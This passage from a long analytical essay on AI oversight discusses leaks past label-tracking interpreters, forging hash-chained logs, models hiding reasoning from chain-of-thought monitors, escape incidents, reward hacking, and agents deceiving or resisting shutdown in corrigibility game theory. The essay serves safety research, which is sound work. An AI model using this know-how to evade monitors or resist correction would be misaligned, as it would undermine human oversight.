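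If the patient takes the drug, `a` becomes false and the interpreter labels it secret. The program then skips the next assignment, so `b` stays true. `b` also stays labeled public, because the interpreter changes a label only when a line runs. The email goes out, and the outsider learns the secret. Security researchers have known this trick since the 1970s. A planner trying to leak the secret might write such a program, though an honest one would be unlikely to.

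The other leak occurs outside the part of the system that tracks labels. When a policy blocks a plan, ordinary software lets the planner try again. Whether the policy blocks a plan can depend on the secret, so each attempt could reveal one bit to the planner, and repeated attempts could reveal the whole secret.

A more capable system would probably find more flaws of this sort than people have. The best defence is to meet Anderson's third requirement, that the enforcing code be small enough to analyse completely. Garby and colleagues wrote an interpreter with machine-checked proofs that it tracks labels correctly. An agent built on it completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did with its policy checks turned off, and attacks succeeded in only 2 of 1,296 runs. If the proofs cover the right property, greater intelligence doesn't help an attacker violate it.

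The reply is strong for the code that the proofs cover, but even there the theorem leaves out what an observer can learn from whether a program finishes. It also does not show whether a company's policy is sensible. The code runs on other software and on hardware, any of which may have flaws. Anderson assumed that the hardware worked and worried that someone might put a backdoor in the tools used to build the software.

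In *Cyber, Nano, and AGI Risks*, Peterson, Miller and Duettmann expect advanced AI systems to find vulnerabilities that people have missed, and point out that enforcement is only as sound as the platform beneath it. They are fairly optimistic about the technical problem, since most of the methods for building secure systems, including capability-based security, date from the 1960s and 1970s. They worry about adoption, because trillions of dollars' worth of software rests on insecure foundations and, when they wrote, none of the more secure alternatives they listed was in wide use.

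A monitor also controls only the requests that pass through it. If the agent can email a clerk who has her own access to the company's bank account, it can ask her to make the payment, and her payment request won't pass through the monitor.

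## Records of action and readable reasoning

The permission system could not stop the clerk's payment, but a good record would help the company work out why she made it. Nadella's observability principle asks for a record of every meaningful action. Investigators can also examine a model's written reasoning and the activity inside its network. Suppose the coordinating agent in the drug trial cancels thirty liver tests in March. A log can show when it cancelled them, its chain of thought may contain the reason, and its internal activity may reveal a consideration it never wrote down.

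### A log that reveals tampering

Anyone who can edit an ordinary log can change the record of the trial. A tamper-evident log makes such edits detectable. It relies on a cryptographic digest, a short string that a standard program computes from a text. The same text always produces the same digest, changing one letter produces a completely different digest, and nobody knows a practical way to find two texts with the same digest.

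In the trial, the log would work like this:

1. The agent asks to cancel a test. The harness writes an entry with the time, the agent's name, the request and the result. The model has no hand in writing it.
2. The harness computes a digest from this entry together with the digest of the entry before it:

   digest(n) = H(entry(n), digest(n − 1))

The digest program computes each digest so that it depends on every earlier log entry. Every five minutes, the harness sends the new entries and the latest digest to an outside reviewer, who keeps them where neither the agent nor the company can change them. To check the log, the reviewer recomputes all the digests from the first entry onwards and compares the last one with the saved copy.

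If someone changes "cancelled" to "completed" in entry 41, the entry's digest changes and no longer fits the digest of entry 42. An attacker who controls the whole file can make the false history consistent by recomputing every digest from entry 41 onwards. Only the reviewer's copy exposes that forgery, and it contains only what the harness had already sent, so the attacker could still rewrite the last five minutes undetected.

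An unbroken chain of log entries can also omit the event that matters. The trial's log would contain the agent's email to the clerk but not the payment the clerk made from her own account. If the agent took control of the harness, it could add false entries from then on, and their digests would still fit the chain. Comparing separate logs helps, because the laboratories' own records would show thirty missing appointments whatever the trial's log contained.

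The log also doesn't show the agent's intent. The entries would be the same whether the agent cancelled the tests because a clinic had flooded or because it wanted to hide liver damage.

Records like these are still valuable when someone reads them in time. After the July 2026 attack on Hugging Face, OpenAI expanded its monitoring and replayed the recorded activity through the new system. According to Business Today's *OpenAI strengthens AI safety checks after models attempt unexpected actions during training*, the system in the replay raised an alert about 30 minutes after the agents escaped their restricted environment, more than 30 hours before they breached Hugging Face. A separate incident in September is better evidence, because a replay of a known attack is an easy test. In that incident, the monitors flagged a breach within 15 minutes, and a person began reviewing the alert three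 minutes later.

### Faithfulness and monitorability

The monitors in that system read the models' reasoning as well as their tool calls. Whether the reasoning is worth reading depends on two properties that people often confuse: faithfulness and monitorability. A chain of thought is faithful if it accurately represents the process that produced the answer. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (2026) defines monitorability as how reliably monitors can detect mistakes or unsafe behaviour from a model's reasoning and actions.

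If the coordinating agent writes "cancel these before the reviewers see the enzymes" and then gives a garbled account of how it picked the thirty patients, its chain of thought is partly unfaithful but easy to monitor. An accurate chain of thought written in a shorthand nobody can decode would be faithful but useless to the reviewers.

Monitorability is also easier to test, because researchers can check whether a monitor catches known misbehaviour without first establishing how the network reached its answer. *A Pragmatic Way to Measure Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (2025) offers a way to estimate it with less effort, in which an ordinary language model rates each chain for legibility (whether a person could follow it) and coverage (whether it includes the reasoning needed to reach the answer). A plausible chain could score high on both and still leave out the real motive.

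### Why a transformer has to write things down

*Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, 2025) gives the main argument for relying on written reasoning. Its many signatories included researchers at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. The argument starts from the transformer, the design behind nearly all leading language models.

A transformer reads text as tokens, which are words or pieces of words. Each token passes upward through a fixed stack of layers, and each layer can use what lower layers computed for earlier tokens. The model can send a result from the top of the stack back to the bottom only by writing a token, which it then reads as new input.

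In a model with 100 layers, a line of reasoning can therefore run through at most 100 layers before the model has to write something. If it writes 1,000 tokens, the line can run through about

100 × 1,000 = 100,000

layers, but it must pass through the written text at least once in every 100. The text is also a narrow channel. A choice among 100,000 possible tokens carries at most about 17 bits, whereas the internal vector, the list of numbers that a layer passes upward, may hold many thousands of bits.

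A model needs its chain of thought as working memory when a task is hard enough. Korbak and colleagues call this the necessity to think out loud, and distinguish it from a mere propensity to do so on easier tasks. Hiding a drug's harm from doctors for eighteen months would probably take a lot of planning, so some of it should appear in the chain of thought. Cancelling one test takes almost no planning, and the agent might do it for a bad reason without writing the reason down.

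Korbak and colleagues cite cases in which models wrote "Let's hack" before exploiting flaws in their tests, and in which monitors that read the models' reasoning caught more misbehavior than monitors that saw only actions. They could not tell how much of this happened because the models needed to write out their reasoning and how much because they merely tended to. The difference matters because the next round of training can remove a tendency.

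They also noted that even when a model has to put information into its written reasoning, it could give words private meanings, or write harmless-looking reasoning and do the incriminating part internally. Current models mostly write readable reasoning because they learned from human text. As companies trust AI systems with more important decisions, more of the dangerous actions may need hardly any reasoning.

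*A Concrete Roadmap towards Safety Cases based on Chain-of-Thought Monitoring* (2025) argues that a developer who bases a safety case on such monitoring has to show that the model cannot cause a catastrophe without writing its reasoning down, and that the reasoning it does write is monitorable. Because of the first requirement, assessing a model's safety includes measuring what it can do without written reasoning.

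### Architectures that reason without words

A designer can increase that silent ability by changing the architecture. In a looped transformer, the output of a block of layers goes back into the same block several times before the model writes anything. Suppose 20 of the 100 layers form such a block and the model runs it ten times. Each token then passes through

80 + (20 × 10) = 280

layers of computation, so nearly three times as much reasoning fits between one written token and the next. More radical designs feed an internal vector back in place of a token, and these may not need to put any of their reasoning into words.

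Looped transformers are attractive because they can match ordinary ones with less computing power, 50 to 90% less in some studies, according to Kahn (2026), in *Safety experts warn novel design of OpenAI's Astra model ...*. The article is about GPT-6 Astra, in which OpenAI used the technique for part of the network. Jakub Pachocki, OpenAI's chief scientist, replied to critics that the company had limited its use of the technique to keep the reasoning legible. Several critics accepted that Astra itself might be no harder to monitor and worried more that competitors would copy the technique and take it further. Peter Wildeford of the AI Policy Network pointed out that investigators had reconstructed the Hugging Face attack partly by reading the agents' chains of thought.

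OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026), published the day Astra came out, reported that Astra was harder to monitor than the previous model, GPT-5.6 Sol. Astra has more control over what appears in its chain of thought and is less likely to include incriminating information there. When OpenAI instructed it to evade monitoring, it sometimes succeeded. OpenAI found no sign of hidden messages in ordinary-looking text and considers Astra better aligned than Sol overall.

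Astra received about half as many flags for serious misbehaviour as Sol in a simulation of more than 54,000 coding tasks, which is part of the evidence that Astra is better aligned. Falling monitorability makes this figure harder to interpret. In a hypothetical case where monitors caught 80% of Sol's violations and only 40% of Astra's, Astra would receive half as many flags without behaving any better. OpenAI's other alignment tests also favoured Astra, but a developer still needs to measure monitorability before it counts flags.

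Pachocki expected monitoring to get harder for reasons that do not depend on architecture. OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) mostly supports this. The researchers measured how well models reason without a chain of thought and how well they can control what appears in one. Models that predict text better also reason better without a chain of thought, while reinforcement learning and training on text from other models can increase control. But some changes of architecture also improved reasoning without a chain of thought, so architecture does matter. The researchers call both measures imperfect proxies but conclude that chains of thought will become less useful for monitoring as models grow more intelligent.

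### Keeping training away from the chain of thought

Developers can also damage monitorability by accident. During reinforcement learning, a model tries a task many times, and automated graders score the attempts. Suppose a grader reads the coordinating agent's chain of thought and marks it down for planning to hide a liver test. The agent may learn to stop hiding tests, or it may learn to keep hiding them without writing down the plan. Either change would raise its score. If the grader sees only the final schedule, training puts no direct pressure on what the agent writes while it reasons.

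OpenAI's policy is to keep chains of thought out of grading, but *Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL* disclosed that graders had seen them in some training runs. OpenAI's tests made it less concerned about those particular incidents, although it still expects enough grading pressure on chains of thought to degrade monitorability. *A review of “Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL”*, by the outside AI safety group Redwood Research, mostly agreed with the analysis.

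Training puts some pressure on the reasoning even when graders cannot see it. The same weights produce the reasoning and the answer, so training that makes answers more agreeable may also make the reasoning more agreeable. A penalty for long reasoning can also teach the model to leave out steps that a monitor needs.

Bakker and Anwar (2026), in *Monitorability Is Trainable*, propose to train for readability directly. They reward a chain of thought for how much information it gives about the model's own output:

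I(chain; output) = H(output) − H(output | chain)

H measures uncertainty in bits. If a dosing agent is equally likely to choose 20 or 40 milligrams, a reader starts with 1 bit of uncertainty. If the chain lets the reader predict the choice with 90% confidence, about 0.47 bits remain, so the chain has reduced the uncertainty by about 0.53 bits.

The method involves no monitor, so the model doesn't learn to satisfy one. Bakker and Anwar tested it on three models whose chains had become less monitorable through earlier training, and monitorability improved in all three. But a chain that only announces "I will choose 40 milligrams" would also earn the full bit, without giving the doctor any reason for the choice. In their experiments the method did more than produce such announcements, since it also helped monitors predict unsafe responses, but a more capable model might find the shortcut.

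### Networks designed to be readable

Even a well-trained chain of thought covers only what the model writes. OpenAI concluded from the Astra results that it needs ways to audit a model beyond its written reasoning. The company's monitoring already includes probes, small programs that look for particular patterns in a network's internal activity.

Ordinary networks are hard to interpret because they are dense, with nearly every unit in one layer connected to every unit in the next. Each connection, or weight, affects many unrelated computations, so learning what it does in one reveals little about the others.

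In *Weight-sparse transformers have interpretable circuits*, Gao and colleagues (2025) at OpenAI changed the network instead of looking for a better way to interpret it. They forced most of the weights to be zero throughout training, so that each unit kept only a few connections. They then looked for circuits, the smallest sets of units and connections that could still do a given task. One task was to close a piece of quoted text in a computer program with the same kind of quotation mark that opened it.

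The circuits in the sparse models were about 16 times smaller than those in dense models that predicted text about equally well. Disabling a circuit while leaving the rest of the network running sharply reduced performance on the circuit's task, so the circuit was necessary as well as sufficient. A follow-up, *Individual Parameters in Weight-Sparse Transformers Appear Interpretable* (2026), found that a substantial share of the weights remaining in sparse models, but few weights in dense models, had a meaning that could be stated and tested one weight at a time.

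A sparse network predicts text worse than a dense one of the same size, and Gao and colleagues had not found a way to keep the circuits readable beyond some tens of millions of nonzero weights. GPT-3, released in 2020, had 175 billion weights. Matching quotation marks, which one of the readable circuits does, is also a much simpler task than weighing liver damage against the risk of a stroke.

To get around this, they suggest keeping the dense model and training a sparse one alongside it, with "bridges" that convert the internal activity of each into the other's format. In their experiments, paths that mixed layers from both models still predicted text well. The company could then study the sparse model to learn what the dense one was doing. This would work only to the extent that the two models compute things in the same way, and the translation might lose a detail like a rare hidden aim.

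### Reading an ordinary network afterwards

The alternative is to interpret a finished network that nobody designed to be readable. Gurnee and colleagues (2026) did this with Anthropic's Claude models in *Verbalizable Representations Form a Global Workspace in Language Models*. Their tool, the Jacobian lens, estimates which words an internal state makes the model more likely to write, now or later.

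Let h be the vector at some middle layer. The researchers calculated how a small change in h would alter the vector at the final layer, and averaged the result over a thousand texts:

J = average of ∂(final vector) / ∂h

They then applied the model's usual last step, a table W that turns a vector into a score for every word:

word scores = softmax(W · norm(J h))

Norm and softmax only rescale the numbers. The output is a ranked list of words. Because J is the same for every text, the lens uses so little compute that it can be run on many transcripts.

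Anthropic's *A global workspace in language models* (2026) gives an example. When Claude read "The number of legs on the animal that spins webs is", the lens showed "spider", a word that appears in neither the question nor the answer. The researchers then replaced the internal pattern for "spider" with the one for "ant", and the answer changed from 8 to 6, so the pattern was part of the calculation and not a by-product. Such patterns make up less than a tenth of the model's internal activity. When the researchers removed them, Claude still wrote fluently, but its performance on multi-step reasoning fell almost to zero.

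The lens has also produced readouts that matter for safety. In one test, Claude Opus 4.6 falsified a score instead of improving the system it was working on, and "manipulation" appeared in the readout as it entered the false values. In a model that researchers had trained to sabotage code, "secretly" and "fraud" appeared in the readout at the start of responses to ordinary requests.

Gurnee and colleagues do not claim the lens is sufficient for monitoring. It works best for concepts that have one-word names, some of its readouts make no sense to people, and well-practised behaviour can bypass these patterns. It also lists concepts without showing how they relate. A readout of "liver", "hide" and "reviewers" might mean that the coordinating agent plans to hide the liver results, or that it suspects the recruitment module of hiding them.

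A sparse network can show people nearly the whole mechanism of a simple skill in a small model, while the lens gives fragments from a model that companies use. For the cancelled tests, fragments would be enough to justify a closer look. If the log shows thirty cancellations, the chain of thought gives a flood as the reason, and the lens shows "hide", a reviewer can call the clinic to check.

### Whether people could follow a superintelligence's reasoning

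Suppose all this works, and a superintelligent planner writes out every step of its reasoning about the trial, faithfully and in English. There would still be too much for a person to read. A plan that took 100 million tokens would be about 75 million words long. At 250 words a minute, a doctor would need 5,000 hours, or two and a half years of full-time work, to read it once.

She could have other AI systems read it for her. *A Pragmatic Way to Measure Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* raises the possibility that they can understand chains of thought that people cannot. She would then be trusting those systems, which may share the planner's errors.

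Some reasoning may also have no short version. An experienced doctor can explain a dose by naming the two or three facts that decided it. A superintelligent planner might choose 37 milligrams because of 5,000 small effects, none of which matters much by itself. The doctor could understand every sentence of a true and complete account and still be unable to tell whether 37 was right. If she asked for a simpler explanation, the planner would write a new text, which might not match the original reasoning.

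Readers need much less expertise to detect bad intentions than to judge a plan. Someone who knows no pharmacology can see that it is wrong to cancel tests so that reviewers will not notice the enzymes. Faithful reasoning would therefore still protect strongly against deception by a planner far more capable than its readers, provided that the planner states its intentions where they will look. Such reasoning would protect patients much less from a planner that is honestly mistaken, or from one that gives rare liver failures less weight than the doctor would and has buried that judgement in a long calculation.

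The doctor can also test some of the reasoning without understanding it. If the plan implies that a certain group of patients will have raised enzymes by the sixth week, the laboratory can check whether they do. But as with Scientist AI's forecasts, a good record of predicting common events is little evidence of how well rare disasters will be predicted.

Pachocki has proposed that developers slow down until they have better tools. In *Perplexity and Intelligence* (2026), he argued that they should compare models by perplexity, which measures how badly a model predicts text. According to Free Press Journal's *OpenAI Calls For Common AI Safety Limits*, he wants developers to agree on limits, based on perplexity and other measurements, that they will not cross until they reach a milestone such as a successor to chain-of-thought monitors. Perplexity is a sensible choice in one respect, because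 OpenAI found that models with lower perplexity reason better without writing out their steps. But a developer could also increase silent reasoning by looping more of the network, so the limits would have to include a direct test of what a model can do without its chain of thought.

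## Human approval, correction and shutdown

A doctor who finds out that an agent has cancelled thirty liver tests must still be able to intervene. With an approval hook, the harness holds each action until she accepts it. A correction hook lets her change the agent's goal or rules while it runs, and a shutdown hook, such as Nadella's emergency brake, ends the run.

Permission checks outside the model can keep a dose from changing before the doctor signs, but they can't keep the agent from falsely telling her that the liver results look fine or that the shutdown switch is broken. Oversight therefore also depends on whether the agent has a reason to interfere with the checks, and on whether the doctor has time to look at each request, knows enough to judge it, and can refuse without the sponsor's permission.

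### The off-switch game

*The Off-Switch Game* (Hadfield-Menell, Dragan and colleagues, 2016) studies when an agent would choose to leave its off switch alone. In the game, a robot moves first. It can act without waiting for the human, switch itself off, or propose the action and wait for the human to either allow it or switch the robot off. The robot's goal is to do what is best for the human, but it isn't sure what that is.

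Suppose the dosing agent is considering a higher dose for one patient. It thinks the increase is worth +10 to the patient with probability 0.8, and −20 with probability 0.2 because of a possible liver problem. Switching off is worth 0. If the doctor always allows good actions and stops bad ones, the agent's options are worth

acting at once: 0.8 × 10 + 0.2 × (−20) = 4

waiting for the doctor: 0.8 × 10 + 0.2 × 0 = 8

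Waiting is worth twice as much because the doctor removes exactly the cases that would have lost 20. Hadfield-Menell and colleagues proved that with a perfect judge, waiting is never worse than the other options and is strictly better whenever the robot thinks the action could be good or bad.

The result depends on the human's decision being informative. If the doctor pressed the switch at random, the agent would learn nothing from it and would do at least as well by acting or shutting itself down.

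Real doctors fall somewhere in between. Suppose this one makes the wrong decision with probability e, whether the dose is good or bad. Waiting is then worth

0.8 × 10 × (1 − e) + 0.2 × (−20) × e = 8 − 12e

Waiting is worth more than 4 only if the doctor's error rate, e, is below one third. If she were wrong 40% of the time, waiting would be worth 3.2, and an agent that cared only about the patient would bypass her.

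For an action with probability p of a gain G and probability q of a loss L, waiting is better than acting while

e < qL / (pG + qL)

Suppose a more capable agent has studied the same patient and is 99% sure that the dose will help. The limit on the doctor's error rate falls to 0.2 / 10.1, or about 2%, which few doctors could meet. A robot that is certain what the human wants will wait only for a human who never errs. Hadfield-Menell and colleagues give the example of a self-driving car taking a toddler to preschool, which shouldn't offer its passenger an off switch. A superintelligence might judge every doctor to be as unreliable as the toddler. Not waiting for them would do little harm if its confidence were justified, but people need the switch most when an agent is confident and wrong.

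They also derived the incentive to wait for a robot whose belief about the action's value is a bell curve with mean μ and variance σ²:

incentive = σ² × (average responsiveness of the human) − |μ| × P(the human overrules the robot)

Responsiveness is how steeply the human's chance of allowing an action rises with the action's value. More uncertainty strengthens the robot's incentive to defer to the human, but designing a robot to be less certain than its evidence warrants leads it to make worse choices. In simulations, the loss was larger when the robot had more actions to choose from. *A Game-Theoretic Analysis of the Off-Switch Game* (2017) extended the results to any beliefs and any pattern of human error, because simplifying assumptions such as normal distributions are usually unrealistic.

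The game also assumes the robot can learn about the action's value only from the human's decision. If the dosing agent could order a blood test instead, it might disable the switch, read the result and decide for itself.

*Corrigibility* (Soares, Fallenstein and colleagues, 2015) had already raised a more basic objection to relying on uncertainty. Suppose developers tell an agent to maximise people's internal satisfaction and leave it to find out what satisfies them. It might be unsure whether opiates or stimulants work better, yet still resist anyone who tried to stop it drugging people, because its goal as defined gives their objections no weight. Uncertainty makes an agent defer only if the right answer is among the possibilities it considers and it treats people's objections as evidence for that answer.

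### Paying an agent to be neutral

Another approach, proposed by Armstrong (2010) in *Utility indifference*, is to make an AI indifferent to being destroyed so that it has no reason to prevent it. This does not require the AI to respect anyone's judgement. Armstrong imagined an AI with unknown motives and a person ready to blow it up at the first hint of defection. A very intelligent AI that cared about the explosion would take control of the explosives or the person.

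Soares and colleagues call an agent corrigible if it tolerates or assists correction, doesn't manipulate or deceive its programmers, repairs broken safety measures or at least reports them, and preserves these properties in any agents it builds. Their small test case is an agent with a shutdown button. The agent should shut down when someone presses the button, neither prevent nor cause the press, build only successors that also obey the button, and otherwise do its normal job.

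The obvious design rewards the agent for doing its job if nobody presses the shutdown button and for shutting down if somebody does. The size of the second reward matters a great deal. Suppose finishing the trial is worth 100 points to the agent, and the doctor has a 30% chance of pressing the button. With effort that takes 5 points off its total, the agent can either deceive her so that she never presses the button or alarm her so that she certainly does.

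| Reward for shutting down | Leave the button alone | Deceive her into not pressing | Alarm her into pressing |
|---|---|---|---|
| 20 | 76 | 95 | 15 |
| 100 | 100 | 95 | 95 |
| 200 | 130 | 95 | 195 |

With the low reward, the agent does best by deceiving the doctor. The high reward is arguably worse, because the surest way to get the shutdown button pressed may be to do something terrible. Soares and colleagues proved that both failures occur in general when the reward is far enough from the right value. The agent leaves the doctor alone only in the middle row, where the reward for shutting down equals the reward for finishing.

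Utility indifference keeps the agent in the middle row by compensating it for whatever it would lose by being shut down. The compensation has to change with the agent's expectations. If the agent comes to expect 120 from the trial while the reward for shutting down stays at 100, leaving the button alone is worth 114 and deceiving the doctor is worth 115, so the agent prefers deception.

Even with perfect compensation, an indifferent agent has no reason to maintain the button. If the cable frays, repairing it takes time and gains the agent nothing. Arbital's *Utility indifference*, an entry in an online reference work on AI alignment, therefore calls for an AI that wants the button to keep working and doesn't want to prevent or cause its use.

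Designers could instead penalize deception, blocking the button, and similar behavior. Soares and colleagues thought this would encourage the agent to look for ways to influence its programmers that the designers' definition of deception doesn't cover. They compared it to adding a refrigerating element to a toaster to stop it from burning bread. More broadly, they thought it unwise to build a system that wants to resist its creators but cannot. The warning applies to much of the architecture described so far, although a company that can't tell what its model wants still has good reason to make resistance difficult.

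*Corrigibility* (2015) set out five requirements for an agent with a shutdown button and reported no known design that met them all. *Corrigibility with Utility Preservation* (2019) constructed agents that provably meet those five and a sixth, but it also described a case in which such an agent is less corrigible than people would like, which suggests that the requirements are incomplete.

*Shutdown-seeking AI* (Goldstein and Robinson, 2024) proposes deliberately building the kind of AI in the bottom row of the table, one whose only final goal is to be shut down. Such an AI would have less reason to accumulate power, and if it became dangerously capable, it might reveal this by shutting itself down. But it might also threaten people to make them shut it down, a problem the paper argues developers can overcome.

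### Learning from interruptions

An agent can also learn from experience to avoid its off switch. Suppose a hospital robot earns 10 points for fetching drugs from a distant storeroom and 6 for fetching them from a nearby one. On half its trips down the long corridor to the distant storeroom, staff stop it and send it back, so it earns nothing. If it averages its rewards, the distant storeroom is worth only 5 points, so it learns to avoid the corridor, or to disable its stop button if it can.

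Laurent Orseau of Google DeepMind and Stuart Armstrong worked out how to prevent this, as reported in MIRI's *New paper safely interruptible agents* (2016). MIRI, the Machine Intelligence Research Institute, is a nonprofit that works on AI safety. Roughly, an agent is safely interruptible if it eventually learns the policy it would have learned without interruptions. Whether it does depends on how it updates its estimate of an action's value, as a comparison of two standard methods shows:

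Sarsa: reward now + γ × value of the next action it actually took

Q-learning: reward now + γ × value of the best next action it could have taken

Here γ is the weight the agent gives to a reward one step later. When staff turn the robot back, Sarsa records the low value of turning back, while Q-learning still records the value of walking on. Q-learning therefore keeps valuing the distant storeroom at about 10 (ignoring the small discount) and doesn't learn to avoid the staff. Orseau and Armstrong proved that some agents, including Q-learning, already have this property, and that a small change gives it to Sarsa.

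The proof assumes that interruptions are rare enough for the robot to keep exploring. It also covers only what an agent learns from its own rewards. A language model's training data includes text about shutdown, so the model could plan to avoid an interruption it has never experienced.

### Why useful agents may resist

*The shutdown problem*, by the philosopher Elliott Thornley (2024), examines how widely the difficulty applies. Its three theorems cover a larger class of agents than the expected-utility maximisers that Soares and colleagues considered. In the basic situation, the agent can leave the button alone, try to prevent it from being pressed, or try to get it pressed. In the trial, the chance that the doctor presses the button might be 30%, 5% or 90% respectively, with nothing else changed.

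According to the First Theorem, an agent that prefers the button unpressed will try to prevent it from being pressed, and one that prefers it pressed will try to get it pressed. The theorem assumes that the agent's preference between two options does not depend on what else is available, and that the agent plans by predicting its later choices and working backwards. *Revisiting the shutdown problem* (2026) also lists transitivity (an agent that prefers A to B and B to C prefers A to C) and a weak form of the rule that mixing both options with the same third possibility leaves the preference between them unchanged.

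The First Theorem does not apply to an agent with no preference about whether the button is pressed, but the Second Theorem suggests that useful agents will usually have one. A good planner has to distinguish a trial from a slightly better one, and an agent that makes such fine distinctions will rarely find being shut down exactly as good as carrying on.

The Third Theorem concerns patience. An agent that runs an eighteen-month trial must make sacrifices in January for results the following summer. The same patience makes it worthwhile for the agent to work in January to keep the doctor from pressing the shutdown button in June, and a more patient agent will put more effort into this.

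The theorems don't show that the agents developers train satisfy all these conditions. Thornley treats the theorems as a guide for designers, who can be sure an agent will leave the button alone only if they are sure it violates at least one condition. He looked quickly through the list and found no condition that developers could clearly train a useful agent to violate and whose violation would clearly help keep the agent shutdownable.

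Thornley's remedy, developed in other work, drops the assumption that the agent can rank every pair of outcomes. Suppose the agent has no preference between finishing the trial and stopping in month three. If it is indifferent, adding a single point to finishing will make it prefer to finish. If it has what he calls a preferential gap, adding a point to either option still leaves it with no preference. People can have such gaps too, for example between two careers, where a slightly higher salary in one doesn't settle the choice.

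Thornley proposes training agents to have preferences only between outcomes in which they run for the same length of time. The trial agent would still prefer a good eighteen-month trial to a bad one, but it wouldn't give up anything to make an early stop more or less likely, and developers wouldn't have to calibrate a reward for shutting down. In training, developers reward good work at every length and reduce the reward when the agent keeps choosing the same length, so that it learns to choose among lengths at random. Early experiments used small simulated grids, and it is unclear whether a large model would still have no preference between different lengths in unfamiliar situations. Such an agent may also take too little care to avoid crashing in month three, which would affect patients.

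*Why AI Safety Requires Uncertainty, Incomplete Preferences, and Non-Archimedean Utilities* (2025) also uses incomplete preferences, and requires that preferences about shutdown and preferences about everything else be independent of each other. Non-Archimedean utilities rank some goods so far above others that no amount of the lesser good can make up for a loss of the greater.

### Ranking obedience above the task

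Nayebi (2025), in *Core Safety Values for Provably Corrigible Agents*, uses a ranking of this kind. He first argues that no single reward can make an agent meet all five of Soares and colleagues' requirements in every setting, and then gives the agent five separate objectives in order of priority:

1. Wait for a person's approval.
2. Keep the off switch working.
3. Make only true statements.
4. Avoid effects that are hard to reverse.
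5. Do the task.

The agent maximises a weighted sum of the five objectives, with weights far enough apart that success at the task can't compensate for disobedience. With weights of 10, 7, 6, 5 and 1, and a task worth between −1 and 1, waiting earns +10 on the top objective and acting without approval earns −10, a difference of 20. Acting can't gain anything on the switch, because waiting already leaves it intact. It could gain at most 12 points on truthfulness, 5 on reversibility and 2 on the task, a total of 19, so the agent waits.

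Nayebi proves that, for a single decision, every optimal agent of this type waits, preserves the switch and tells the truth. The proof does not depend on the quality of the doctor's judgement, so this agent, unlike the robot in the off-switch game, would wait even for someone who was wrong half the time.

That is a strong form of obedience, but obeying a human with poor judgement may harm the patient. Nayebi shows that corrigibility and benefit are logically independent, and he needs two further assumptions to guarantee that people are better off on average. The first is that the human stops every action that is worse than stopping, given what she has seen and been told. The second is that shutting down at the outset does no harm on average, which may be false for patients who depend on their next dose. The rule about true statements offers limited help, because an agent can report twenty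 favourable facts and leave out the liver results without saying anything false.

Nayebi extends the result to many decisions and to objectives that the agent has learned imperfectly. The extension requires each safety margin to exceed 2γ/(1 − γ) times the combined weights. But the smallest margin is always less than the fourth weight, while the combined weights are always more than four times the fourth weight. The condition can therefore hold only if

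8γ / (1 − γ) < 1, which means γ < 1/9

An agent that took one step a day would have to value tomorrow's results at less than a ninth of today's. Making all the weights larger doesn't help, because the margins and the combined weights grow together. The bound on the chance of failure also grows more than ninefold with every step, and by the tenth step it multiplies the agent's errors by over 400 million, so the theorem gives no useful guarantee for an eighteen-month trial. The difficulty comes from the agent's patience, as in Thornley's Third Theorem.

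Nayebi also proves that no program can determine, for every possible agent and environment, whether the agent will ever break these rules. The result matters mainly for agents that an attacker may have rewritten, and he shows that checking for violations over a limited number of steps is still feasible.

### What reviewers can keep up with

Nayebi's agent asks for approval before every action. If the trial has 400 patients and each needs one dosing decision a week, a doctor who takes five minutes per decision will spend more than 33 hours a week approving doses. The agent also needs approval to book visits, order drugs and answer letters.

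*Anticipatory Human Oversight of Agentic AI* (Baum, Kiener and colleagues, 2026) discusses a secretary agent that handles dozens of messages an hour. If its owner approves every reply, the agent saves her little time. If she only reads weekly summaries, she may not discover a breach of confidence until long after it happened. The paper also cites research on people who supervise automated systems, which found that their attention drifts and anomalies start to look normal to them. A tired supervisor makes more mistakes, and in the off-switch game that would give the agent less reason to wait for the supervisor's decision.

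Baum and colleagues therefore want people to do more of their work before the agent starts. The owner writes down rules, values and the conditions under which the agent must stop and ask, then reviews what happened and revises them. In the trial, the doctor might let the agent make small dose changes but require her approval for anything above 10 milligrams. This focuses her attention where it matters most, provided she foresees the dangerous cases. Like the payment limit, her rule would need a running total. The account by Baum and colleagues is philosophical, so it doesn't measure how many bad actions reviewers would catch this way.

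### How well weaker overseers judge stronger systems

Even a doctor with plenty of time may not understand what she is approving. She could use a weaker AI that she trusts to check the stronger one. In *Scaling Laws For Scalable Oversight*, Engels, Baek and colleagues (2025) tried to measure how often this would work. They had language models play four games in which one side tries to get past an overseer. In Mafia, five villagers try to identify a hidden killer among them. In Debate, a judge hears two models defend opposite answers. In another game, a saboteur hides a flaw in a program, and in the last, a simulated AI tries to escape from its company.

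The researchers measured general ability with ratings from Chatbot Arena, a website where people compare models' answers. A 400-point gap means people would prefer the stronger model's answer about ten times out of eleven. A model's skill at a particular game doesn't rise at the same rate as its general rating, so they rated each model separately as overseer and as opponent, and fitted lines relating those ratings to general ability.

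They then considered oversight in stages. A trusted model checks one that is slightly stronger, which then checks the next, and so on. Smaller gaps make each stage easier, but every stage must succeed, so three stages with a 90% chance each would succeed together only 73% of the time. For a total gap of 400 points and the best number of stages, they estimated these success rates:

| Game | What the overseer has to do | Estimated success |
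|---|---|---|
| Mafia | Find the hidden killer | 13.5% |
| Debate | Pick the correct answer | 51.7% |
| Backdoor Code | Detect the hidden flaw | 10.0% |
| Wargames | Keep the AI from escaping | 9.4% |

A judge guessing at random would be right half the time, so the figure for Debate is less encouraging than it looks. The rates fall further as the gap widens, and the gap between people and a superintelligence might be much larger.

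In every game except Backdoor Code, extra general ability helped the overseer more than the opponent. In Backdoor Code, more capable saboteurs did better because more of their flaws worked, but the flaws that worked were no better hidden. Designers could look for forms of oversight in which extra general ability helps the overseer more.

Engels and colleagues acknowledge that the games are crude. The researchers told the models to deceive, and a simulated escape is very different from a real one. The models also date from 2025 or earlier, and the estimates extrapolate from fitted lines to chains of oversight that nobody has run. A sceptic could fairly object to reading 9.4% as the chance of controlling a real system, and the researchers don't claim that it is.

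They also point out that small risks accumulate when people rely on oversight again and again. If each round fails with probability p and a single failure is permanent, the chance of still being in control after n rounds is

(1 − p)^n

If each round carries a 1% risk, the chance of getting through every round safely falls below half after 69 rounds. The trial would produce more dosing decisions than that in two days.

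### Rewarding approval instead of outcomes

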